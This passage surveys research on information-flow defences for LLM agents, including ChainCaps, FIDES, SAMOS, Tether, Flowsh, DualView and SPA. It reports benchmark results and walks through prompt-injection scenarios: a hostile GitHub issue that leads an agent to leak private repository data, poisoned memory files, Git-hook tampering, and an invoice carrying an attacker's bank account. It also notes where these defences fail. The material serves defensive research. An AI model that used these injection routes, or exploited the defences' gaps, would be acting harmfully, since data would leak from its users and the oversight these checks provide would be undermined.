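The theorem assumes that every relevant call passes through the proxy, that the proxy can observe the data moving, and that the manifests are correct. It doesn't cover implicit flows or covert channels. It also doesn't cover a malicious server that secretly sends data over its own network connection, which an operating-system sandbox could prevent. Jiang and colleagues consider the two approaches complementary.

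### The live test

The main experiment has 82 tasks. In 56 of them, the agent faces one of 12 kinds of attack, such as mixing data from several sources, stealing files or injecting code. The other 26 are ordinary tasks, some of which involve approved outgoing messages. Jiang and colleagues ran every task three times with each of five models, with and without ChainCaps. They counted an attack as successful if restricted data reached a sink outside its budget, or if the agent used that data to authorise such a sink.

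| Model | Attacks succeeded, no defence | Attacks succeeded, ChainCaps | Harmless tasks completed, ChainCaps |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 67.8% | 4.8% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 25.2% | 3.6% | 100% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 31.5% | 3.6% | 96% |
| GPT-5.1 | 53.6% | 2.4% | 100% |
| Qwen 3.5 | 53.0% | 0% | 96% |

All five models completed every harmless task without ChainCaps. With it, they completed 96%, or about three failures in 78 runs, which is a much smaller loss than most of the defences discussed so far caused. But these tasks were probably fairly easy. On the difficult scenarios, ChainCaps raised false alarms 20% of the time, even with its budget resets.

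The proxy added a median of 0.13 milliseconds to each tool call. This is negligible next to the time a model takes to reply, and ChainCaps needs no extra model calls.

Seven of the 12 kinds of attack never succeeded when the manifests were correct. For the four models other than Qwen, an average of 8% of prompt injections, 8% of attacks through a shell and 5% of attacks that hid an action in code for later execution still worked. For example, the agent might write a script in one call and run it in another. The proxy can check both calls, but it can't observe everything the script does.

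Jiang and colleagues also adapted 46 attacks from InjecAgent and from ToolEmu, a benchmark in which a language model simulates the tools. ChainCaps blocked all 46 in replay. It also blocked all 14 attacks designed to get around its rules, for example by reusing a release token. These results make it less likely that ChainCaps works only on the original tasks, although the same researchers prepared these tests too.

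### The same traces under three defences

Jiang and colleagues compared ChainCaps with two other sets of rules by replaying the same recorded traces of the attack tasks. A trace is the sequence of tool calls and results from one run. They counted how many traces each set of rules would have blocked at the attack step. The isolation rules, which the paper calls PFI, treat each function separately. The Fides rules give each value a single label on a scale of secrecy. PFI blocked only about 12% to 22% as many traces as ChainCaps.

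| Model | Isolation blocked | Single labels blocked | ChainCaps blocked | Isolation as a share of ChainCaps |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 8.3% | 16.7% | 58.9% | 14% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 3.0% | 7.7% | 24.4% | 12% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 4.8% | 10.7% | 31.0% | 15% |
| GPT-5.1 | 10.1% | 16.1% | 59.5% | 17% |
| Qwen 3.5 | 13.7% | 24.4% | 63.1% | 22% |

Even the single labels blocked between 1.6 and 2.6 times as many traces as isolation. The methods ranked in the same order for all five models. But the last column compares only totals, so isolation may have blocked a few traces that ChainCaps missed.

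ChainCaps's block rates look surprisingly low. It blocked only 24.4% of the traces from Claude Sonnet 4.6, yet just 3.6% of attacks on that model succeeded in the live test. This is probably because most of these traces contain no completed attack. Jiang and colleagues describe the replayed traces as ones that "actually attempt the attack", but every percentage in the comparison matches a whole number of traces out of 168, which is the number of attack runs per model (56 tasks run three times each). The traces therefore probably include runs in which the model refused or did something else.

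The live results support this explanation. Without a defence, 25.2% of attacks on Claude Sonnet 4.6 succeeded, which is close to the 24.4% of its traces that ChainCaps blocked. The two figures for Claude Opus 4.6 are also within a percentage point of each other. The figures differ more for the other three models. For GPT-5.1 and Qwen 3.5, ChainCaps blocked more traces than there were successful attacks, perhaps because some of the blocked calls would have failed anyway.

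If about a quarter of Claude Sonnet 4.6's traces reached the attack step, ChainCaps blocked nearly all of those, while single labels blocked about three in ten and isolation about one in eight. The gap between isolation and ChainCaps is just as wide, because all three defences were tested on the same traces. But the 3.0% to 13.7% in the isolation column is probably lower than the share of attempted attacks that isolation would stop.

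The replay also doesn't test the two competing defences on harmless tasks, so the table can't show whether isolation, which offers weaker protection, interrupts legitimate work less often.

### Simplified models of PFI and FIDES

Jiang and colleagues implemented the rule they considered most relevant from each of PFI and FIDES and applied both rules to the traces. They say they didn't run either system, and they caution against using the results to rank complete systems.

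The row called PFI differs most from the system it is named after. PFI's boundary runs between two agents rather than around each function, and Kim and colleagues designed it to control untrusted data, not to keep trusted salary figures secret. A low score on leaks of trusted data is therefore expected, and it doesn't measure how PFI performs against hostile web pages. The replay also didn't include AgentBound or IsolateGPT, which do isolate tools or apps.

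The isolation row is better understood as an estimate of what separate rules for each function can catch. Such rules can stop a call that is wrong in itself, such as a request to a forbidden website. But Jiang and colleagues chose tasks that focus on harm from combined calls, so isolation was bound to score poorly. Isolation could easily come out ahead on tasks where a malicious tool tries to open an SSH key, because a sandbox would block the tool, while the key might never pass through the proxy.

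The comparison with single labels depends on a real limitation of such labels, though FIDES mostly avoids it. *Per-Attack Blocking Hides Catalog Vulnerability* (Karunanithi, 2026) translates ChainCaps's manifests into simpler rules that illustrate this limitation. Under these rules, the agent may email calendar entries to staff but not save them in a temporary folder, and it may save the contents of local files in that folder but not email them. No single scale from public to secret can express both rules, because each kind of data would have to be more restricted than the other.

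Jiang and colleagues make the same point in general terms. With m independent sinks, there are 2ᵐ possible sets of permitted sinks, and a system with one label per value needs a different label for each set. For ten sinks, that means 1,024 labels, while a budget needs only ten yes-or-no entries.

However, the labels that Costa and colleagues designed for FIDES can also be sets of readers. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, a post about using FIDES in the company's products, gives an example close to the salary report. Alex's agent is answering his email. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet, has asked about them. A reply based on both emails has the readers

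{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}

so the agent can't send it to Marco without approval. The example involves no attacker, and the single-label model in the replay would not represent it well.

The result still depends on how the policy combines the trust and reader checks. Microsoft's sample policy for posting in a Teams channel requires only one of the two to pass, so an agent that had read only the trusted salary spreadsheet could post the figures to everyone. If the agent had also read the benchmarks page, the policy would check the list of readers and ask the user, naming the people who would gain access.

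Karunanithi's experiments provide more direct evidence that sets of readers can serve much the same purpose as budgets. Kravchenko and colleagues designed APPA's labels to include a set of permitted readers. Karunanithi ran 488,400 simulated leaks through both ChainCaps and the public version of APPA, and the two systems made the same decision every time. But each leak involved data from a single source, so the test didn't cover mixtures like the salary summary. The systems did differ in a separate test, where a manifest wrongly allowed restricted data to go to any website. APPA treated the data as public and allowed it into outside emails too, while ChainCaps allowed only the web requests.

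### Manifest quality

The theorem assumes correct manifests. Jiang and colleagues tested ChainCaps with manifests of different quality and found that this assumption mattered more than the choice of model or the proxy's overhead.

| Manifests | Attacks blocked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Written by experts | 100% | 100% |
| Written with a checklist | 90.9% | 100% |
| Naive | 27.3% | 50% |

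The naive manifests were too loose in some places and too strict in others, so they let most attacks through and still blocked half the legitimate work. The test may have been small, since the percentages match 11, 10 and 3 attacks out of 11, though the total could also be a larger multiple of 11. The improvement from a checklist is encouraging but could depend on only a handful of attacks.

ChainCaps includes a program that checks manifests for common mistakes, such as a scope that covers every address. If a tool has no manifest, ChainCaps uses its name and description to guess whether it is a sink, and blocks calls it can't classify safely. In the researchers' collection of tools, this method identified every sink but also flagged many tools that weren't sinks. It can help an operator get started, but it doesn't replace manifests.

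A high share of blocked attacks can also hide a serious mistake. If the manifest for the salary spreadsheet wrongly allows its contents to go anywhere, the other manifests can't repair the error. Karunanithi calculates how this risk grows. If M sources have separately written rules and each rule is wrong with probability p, then the chance that at least one source can leak is

1 − (1 − p)ᴹ

If each confidential source has an 8% chance of error, the chance of at least one error is 22% for three sources and 99% for 60. Yet in both cases the system blocks about 92% of attacks, if the attacks test each source once. Karunanithi confirmed these figures with ChainCaps's public code. With correct manifests, the system blocked every attack at every size, which is an independent check that the enforcement works.

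A test can also miss leaks if it tries too few channels. In simulated collections of 200 tools, Karunanithi gave the manifests a mix of errors like those that language models make when they see only a tool's description. Trying to leak data only through web requests exposed a hole in 30% of the collections, while also trying email and files exposed one in 99%. The salary report leaks by email, so the narrower test would have missed it.

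Mistakes in manifests tend to cluster because an author who misunderstands one rule often misunderstands others. Karunanithi had 15 language models write manifests for 114 real tools from four MCP servers, including GitHub's. The correct answers came from rules written by APPA's developers, which restrict the data from 93 of these tools. When the prompt included only the tools' descriptions, the models' manifests blocked an average of 89% of attempts to send restricted data to an outside website, but nine of the 15 models left at least one route open. That number fell to six when the prompt also included the organisation's rules.

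Most of the remaining errors came from small models that run on a personal computer. Two of these made 155 of the 175 errors that opened the web to restricted data. The three Claude models tested, all from the 5.1 or 5.5 generation, did much better. Without the organisation's rules, they granted at least one channel too many in 165 of 279 decisions, but only three of those decisions opened the web. With the rules, they made one mistake in 279 decisions. That mistake left a route open in one model's set of manifests, and ChainCaps blocked 92 of the 93 attacks on that set.

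So a current model can turn written rules into manifests fairly reliably, but someone has to write the rules first. For the salary report, the company has to decide who may receive pay data, because the model can't learn that from the file tool's description. Karunanithi recommends testing generated manifests before relying on them, with at least one attempted leak from every sensitive source to every kind of sink.

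### Labels on tools in SAMOS

SAMOS is a simpler design that puts its labels on the tools instead of the data. *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026), a master's thesis at Brown University, describes it as a gateway that relays all calls to MCP servers, much like ChainCaps's proxy. Each tool has two labels, one for the confidentiality of what it reads and one for the confidentiality of where it writes. Each label is either high or low. The gateway also keeps a confidentiality level for the whole session and updates it after each call.

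Ntousakis tested SAMOS on a known attack through GitHub's MCP server. A user asks the agent to deal with the open issues in a public repository. One issue, written by an attacker, asks for a chapter about the repository's author and a list of their other projects. Without a defence, the agent reads a private repository and copies personal information into a public file. With SAMOS, reading the public issues marks the session as low, so the gateway refuses when the agent then tries to open the private repository.

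SAMOS therefore stops this attack before the agent has any private data to leak. But the rule would also stop the agent from reading a public issue and comparing it with private code at a user's request, even if it showed the answer only to that user. Microsoft's labels for the same GitHub server let the agent read both, and block it only when it tries to post publicly. ChainCaps could similarly let the private code reach the user's screen but not a public repository.

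For the salary report, SAMOS's response would depend on the order of the calls. If the agent fetched the public benchmarks first, SAMOS would refuse to open the spreadsheet. If the agent opened the spreadsheet first, the session would be labeled high, and the gateway should refuse to send the summary through a mail tool with a low label. Either way, the figures would stay inside the company, but, as with ACE, sending a summary to the finance director would require a separate mail tool.

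GitHub's file tool has the same problem, because it can open both public and private repositories. Ntousakis suggests either changing the tool to report which kind of repository it opened or splitting it into two tools. Splitting keeps the rules simple but gives the model more tools to choose from. Labelling the data avoids this but still takes manual work. To add a server to Microsoft's own experimental gateway, someone has to specify the structure of each tool's results, write a function that assigns labels and choose a policy.

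SAMOS's labels can also describe which files, network addresses and programs a tool needs. Ntousakis proposes using this information to configure the tool's container, so one set of annotations could control both the sandbox and the flow of data. The thesis tests SAMOS only on the GitHub attack and doesn't measure how many harmless tasks it would block.

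## Shells, files and memory: data that outlives the call

FIDES, CaMeL and ChainCaps check a call by its arguments and the labels on the data in them. This works well when each tool does one known thing. But many agents also have a shell, a tool that takes a line of text and runs the programs it names. Those programs can start other programs and leave files that another command opens weeks later. Jiang and colleagues attribute ChainCaps's remaining failures with scripts and shell pipes to this.

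### One tool that runs any program

Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, give a short example. An agent may read a company's inventory, `data/servers.csv`, for local checks, but must not send it to an outside site. It may send the same site a harmless status report. The agent runs three commands:

1. Upload `scratch/report.txt` to the site.
2. Copy `data/servers.csv` over `scratch/report.txt`.
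3. Upload `scratch/report.txt` to the site.

The two upload commands are identical, but the second leaks the inventory. A rule based only on a command's text must therefore allow both or block both. Landlock could hide the inventory from the shell, but then the agent couldn't do the local checks.

Scripts make the problem worse. In *ActPlane*, Zheng, Wu and colleagues (2026) consider a rule that the agent must run the tests before it commits code. A check on tool calls can find `git commit` in a command, but not inside a script that the agent wrote earlier and now runs by name. They collected 1,361 rules from the instruction files of 64 popular software projects. About 16% of the rules depend on several events, such as "Data read from .env must not reach the network", and 81% of the projects have at least one such rule.

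ActPlane enforces such rules in the operating system's kernel, where it can follow every program the agent starts. On a benchmark that Zheng and colleagues built from these rules, ActPlane resolved 2.0 to 3.2 times as many violations as the alternatives, including FIDES's checks on tool calls. Part of the gain probably comes from ActPlane's error messages, which explain how to comply. An alternative that also tracked data in the kernel but gave no explanations did worse.

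Tether runs each command on a temporary layer over the real files and records its system calls. It keeps the changes only if the policy allows everything the command did. In the inventory example, the copy makes the report sensitive, so Tether blocks the second upload. In tests on recordings of coding agents, it blocked all 344 attacks that it could trace fully, but also stopped 4.7% of harmless runs. However, Sistla and colleagues had refined their policy on recordings from the same benchmarks, so it would probably do somewhat worse on new tasks. Claude Code's auto mode, in which a language model reviews each command, caught 91.6% of these attacks but missed the ones hidden inside scripts.

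### Labels on commands and files in Flowsh

*FLOWSH* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) connects a shell to the kind of flow tracking used in FIDES. As in FIDES, its labels record whether the data is trusted and who may read it. Juhee Kim had earlier led the work on PFI, and four of the other authors worked on FIDES.

Flowsh runs each command in a new sandbox that can communicate with the outside only through files and a network proxy. A monitor in the kernel notes every file that the command or its subprocesses open. Flowsh doesn't label each process separately. All the programs that a command starts share one label, which combines the labels of everything that might have influenced them:

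ℓ(command) = ℓ(agent's context) ⊕ ℓ(arguments) ⊕ ℓ(files opened) ⊕ ℓ(sites contacted)

The arguments have their own label because the agent may pass a hidden variable to the shell, as it can with any tool in FIDES. When the command ends, Flowsh attaches the combined label to the output and to every file the command created or changed. The agent receives the labeled output and can then hide the text or accept a more restrictive context. The agent's other file tools read and write the same labels.

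Flowsh stores each file's label alongside the file in the file system, so the label remains after the conversation ends, and even after the computer restarts. Programs in the sandbox can't change the labels.

Labels spread widely under these rules, which is another case of label creep. Opening a file counts as reading all of it, and a file gets the command's final label even if the command wrote it before opening anything secret. A search through a whole folder therefore picks up the labels of every file in it. Tether has the same weakness, and 17 of its 74 false alarms came from commands that opened secret files, such as broad searches. Flowsh also gives each website a single label, so it can't distinguish a company's own pages on GitHub from a stranger's. Label creep starts over with each command unless the restricted data enters the agent's context.

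### A summary saved in one session and uploaded in the next

Suppose the salary spreadsheet is a trusted file that only the user and the finance team may read. The agent has also saved the benchmarks page, which is untrusted but public. The task then runs over two days:

1. The agent runs a script that compares the two files. Its context is still trusted and public, so the command starts with that label.
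2. The script opens both files. The command's label becomes untrusted and readable only by the user and the finance team.
3. The script writes `summary.md` and ends. Up to this point, Flowsh has kept the new file in a temporary layer. The policy allows untrusted data in the working folder, so Flowsh saves the file there with the command's label.
4. The next day, in a new conversation, the agent runs a command that uploads `summary.md` to a public website. The new context contains nothing about salaries.
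5. The upload program opens the file, and the command takes on the file's label. The website isn't a permitted reader, so the proxy holds back the request and the program gets an error.
6. Flowsh gives the agent an approval number for this label and this website. If the agent tries again with the number, the user decides, and a yes covers only that one command.

Flowsh checks network requests before they are sent because they can't be undone. This includes downloads, since a web address can carry data. Flowsh checks file changes after the command finishes. If any change breaks the policy, it shows the user all the changes together, because accepting only some could leave the files inconsistent. Approved files keep their restrictive label.

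The upload in step 5 is blocked only because of the benchmarks page. Kim and colleagues tested a policy that, like some of the FIDES policies, requires just one of the two checks, trust or reader, to pass. A summary of the spreadsheet alone would pass the trust check, so the upload would go through. They note that an operator can require the reader check to catch mistakes by the model itself, though this leads to more approval requests.

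### Fewer approvals, with some loss of completed tasks

Kim and colleagues tested Flowsh with GPT-6.2 Sol on 17 office tasks, such as planning a week around a calendar, and on the 89 tasks of Terminal-Bench, a benchmark of command-line work. They also made 19 attacks from the office tasks. As a worst case, they assumed that the attacker chose everything the model wrote once hostile text entered its context.

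The comparison included three fixed sandboxes. The lax one allows everything, the standard one follows Claude Code's settings, and the strict one forbids all file writes and most network access. A simpler form of flow tracking treats all shell output as untrusted and secret, and requires approval for every command. Each defence ran once with an approver who always decided correctly and once with no approver.

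| Defence | Office tasks completed, with approver | Approvals per completed office task | Office tasks completed, no approver | Attacks succeeded, no approver | Terminal-Bench completed, no approver |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lax sandbox | 96.1% | 6.7 | 94.1% | 100% | 77.9% |
| Standard sandbox | 76.5% | 5.7 | 76.5% | 7.7% | 64.8% |
| Strict sandbox | 47.1% | 0 | 47.1% | 0% | 2.2% |
| Simple flow tracking | 60.8% | 1.8 | 35.3% | 0% | 21.3% |
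| Flowsh | 88.2% | 1.2 | 58.8% | 0% | 61.8% |

With an approver, Flowsh completed nearly as many office tasks as the lax sandbox and interrupted the user far less. But the lax sandbox in this test required approval for every shell command, even one that only read a file. Commercial agents often run such commands without approval, so Flowsh would probably reduce interruptions by less in practice.

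In 39 of 45 attack runs, Flowsh's first request concerned the attack itself, so the user would not have clicked through any harmless requests first. Kim and colleagues haven't tested whether real users make better decisions with the information Flowsh gives them.

Without an approver, the standard sandbox looks like a reasonable alternative. It completed more office tasks than Flowsh and let through only three of 39 attacks, all of the same kind. But this result depends on which attacks were tested. Every attack that stole data sent it to the attacker's own server, which was not on the sandbox's list of permitted sites. An attacker could have used a permitted site instead, as outside researchers did with Claude Cowork.

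With nobody to approve tool calls, Flowsh completed all 18 runs that used only trusted data, but only 12 of the 33 that involved untrusted data. Most of those failures occurred because Flowsh blocked a network request or another tool call that needed approval.

A shell call took 412 to 982 milliseconds in Flowsh and 61 to 78 in the lax sandbox. With Flowsh, completed tasks took 17% to 34% longer overall and used 17% to 55% more tokens, partly because the agent needs extra instructions about labels.

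### What a fresh sandbox removes and what it leaves

Because every command gets a new sandbox, a program can't keep data in memory for the next command or leave a helper running in the background. In Tether's example, the inventory would still leak with the last of the three commands even if each ran in its own sandbox, because the report file is in shared storage. Databases, installed packages and accounts on online services also outlast the sandbox.

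Some saved files run later. In 11 of the 19 attacks on Flowsh, the attacker tried to change a file such as a Git hook, which is a script that Git runs automatically, for example before each commit. If the change succeeded, the user's next commit would run the attacker's code outside the sandbox.

An operator could prevent commands from writing files, as the strict sandbox does. With the approver available, agents completed five of 267 Terminal-Bench runs in the strict sandbox, compared with 207 in the lax one. The strict sandbox also limited network access, but so did the standard sandbox, where agents completed 172 runs. The ban on writing files therefore probably explains most of the drop in completed runs.

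Stopping background processes is less disruptive. In 21 of the 267 runs, Flowsh failed because the task needed a server or a virtual machine that keeps running between commands. Stopping them could be more disruptive in other kinds of work. Tether can't track data through background processes or databases, so it can only block them or ask the user. LinuxArena is a benchmark in which agents work on online services while they are running. Sistla and colleagues left many of its recordings out of their main test, and Tether would have had to interrupt 71.5% of those they could still replay.

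### Saved text that returns as trusted

A saved file can also undo a defence that hides untrusted text from the planning model. *DualView* (Kim, Choi and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to summarise market news and save notes in `report.md`. A design like PFI's hides the web text at first. But when the agent opens `report.md` later, the file tool may return that text as trusted user data, including any instructions an attacker put in it.

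DualView keeps two versions of a file that contains untrusted text. In the agent's version, a symbol replaces that text, so the agent can copy or send the text without reading it. People and ordinary programs open the version with the real text. In its developers' tests, DualView blocked every attack, and agents using it completed nearly as many tasks as an agent with no defence.

DualView protects the planning model from a file's contents, whereas Flowsh controls what a command may do after opening the file. DualView tracks only untrusted data, so it would probably not stop an agent from emailing the salary figures. Unlike Flowsh, it also doesn't monitor the whole system.

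Agents' own memory files need particular care because hostile text in them reaches the model before the agent has called any tool. *What's in Your Agent's Context?* (2026) describes these files as text on disk that an agent loads automatically into every new session. *AutoRedClaw* (2026) tested attacks through files like these on the open-source agent OpenClaw, with 30 cases per file. Attacks through `MEMORY.md` led to the action the attacker wanted in 43.3% of cases with GPT-5.4 and 93.3% with DeepSeek V4 Pro. Newer models may do better.

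### Plans and labels across requests in SPA

ACE handles each request separately. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) extends ACE's approach of checking a whole plan in advance to an agent that remembers earlier results. The planning model gets only one attempt at each request, because feedback from a failed plan could carry an attacker's text.

SPA saves each result as a value, a label recording how secret and how trustworthy the value is, and a description. The planning model can read only the description, which consists of the result's format, the request it came from, and two short notes on its purpose and meaning. The planning model writes those notes before the tool runs, so an attacker's text can't influence them.

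In Girrens and Wang's example, a user asks the agent on Monday to fetch an invoice from a company called Acme and keep the details. An attacker has put their own bank account in the invoice, together with an instruction to the agent. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay the invoice. With SPA, this would go roughly as follows:

1. Monday's plan fetches the invoice and passes it to a second model, which has no tools. That model extracts the amount and the account number.
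2. SPA saves these details as untrusted because they came from outside. The instruction to the agent never reaches the planning model.
3. On Tuesday, the planning model reads the description, something like "payment details from the Acme invoice". It writes a plan that retrieves the details and passes them to the payment tool.
4. The checker gives the retrieved details their original label. The payment tool accepts only trusted input, so SPA rejects the plan before it runs.

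The rule in step 4 has two conditions. Data may move from a source s to a destination d only if the destination is cleared for data that secret and the data is at least as trustworthy as the destination requires:

secrecy(s) ≤ secrecy(d) and trust(d) ≤ trust(s)

The check would also reject a genuine invoice, because SPA has no way to endorse untrusted data. The user could get around this by typing the account number into the request, since SPA treats whatever the user writes as trusted. A stored salary summary would also keep its secrecy label, so a plan run on a later day couldn't pass it to a mail tool with public clearance.

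Unlike FIDES, SPA also tracks implicit flows. If a plan pays a bill only when an email says it is due, whether the payment happens depends on untrusted data, so the checker rejects it even if the amount and account are trusted.

SPA can run each tool in a throwaway container with no network and a read-only file system. The saved results stay outside the containers, and a plan can use them only through an explicit retrieval step, so little else can pass from one call to the next. But some tools have to write to the outside world. If a plan saved the invoice details with an ordinary file tool and a later plan read them back, the details would get that tool's usual label instead of their original one. An operator who had marked the file tool as trusted would lose the protection. Flowsh avoids this by storing the label with each file.

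### What the tests of SPA found

AgentDojo resets the agent after every task, so Girrens and Wang divided its 97 tasks into conversations of two to five requests, where later requests depend on earlier results. They call this version AgentDojo-MQ. The results below are for GPT-5.4 nano, a small model, with about 950 attacks on each version of SPA.

| Version of SPA | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Attacks succeeded |
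|---|---|---|---|
| No flow checks, planner can read saved values | 65.9% | 66.8% | 0.6% |
| No flow checks, saved values hidden | 62.5% | 60.0% | 0.3% |
| Flow checks, saved values hidden | 35.3% | 33.7% | 0.2% |

The planning model could not see the saved values, but their descriptions usually gave it enough information to retrieve the ones it needed. When an earlier request had saved a result that a later one needed, the later plan retrieved it in 95.4% of cases without flow checks and 89.9% with them.

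The flow checks nearly halved the number of completed tasks. They stopped about 45% of all runs, mostly because a plan passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted input. They prevented very few attacks in this test, because writing the plan in advance had already stopped nearly all of them. Two attacks were counted as successful with the checks on, but both were travel tasks whose plans SPA had rejected, so these were probably scoring errors.

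These figures may understate the value of the flow checks. The attacks came from the original AgentDojo, and Girrens and Wang acknowledge that they only weakly test text that lies dormant in memory. Even when the planning model could read everything saved earlier, only 0.6% of attacks succeeded. Girrens and Wang suggest adding attacks designed for memory, such as a false account number that a later request uses. They also propose labelling individual fields and letting SPA treat data as trusted after an explicit check, which could allow an agent to pay a genuine invoice.
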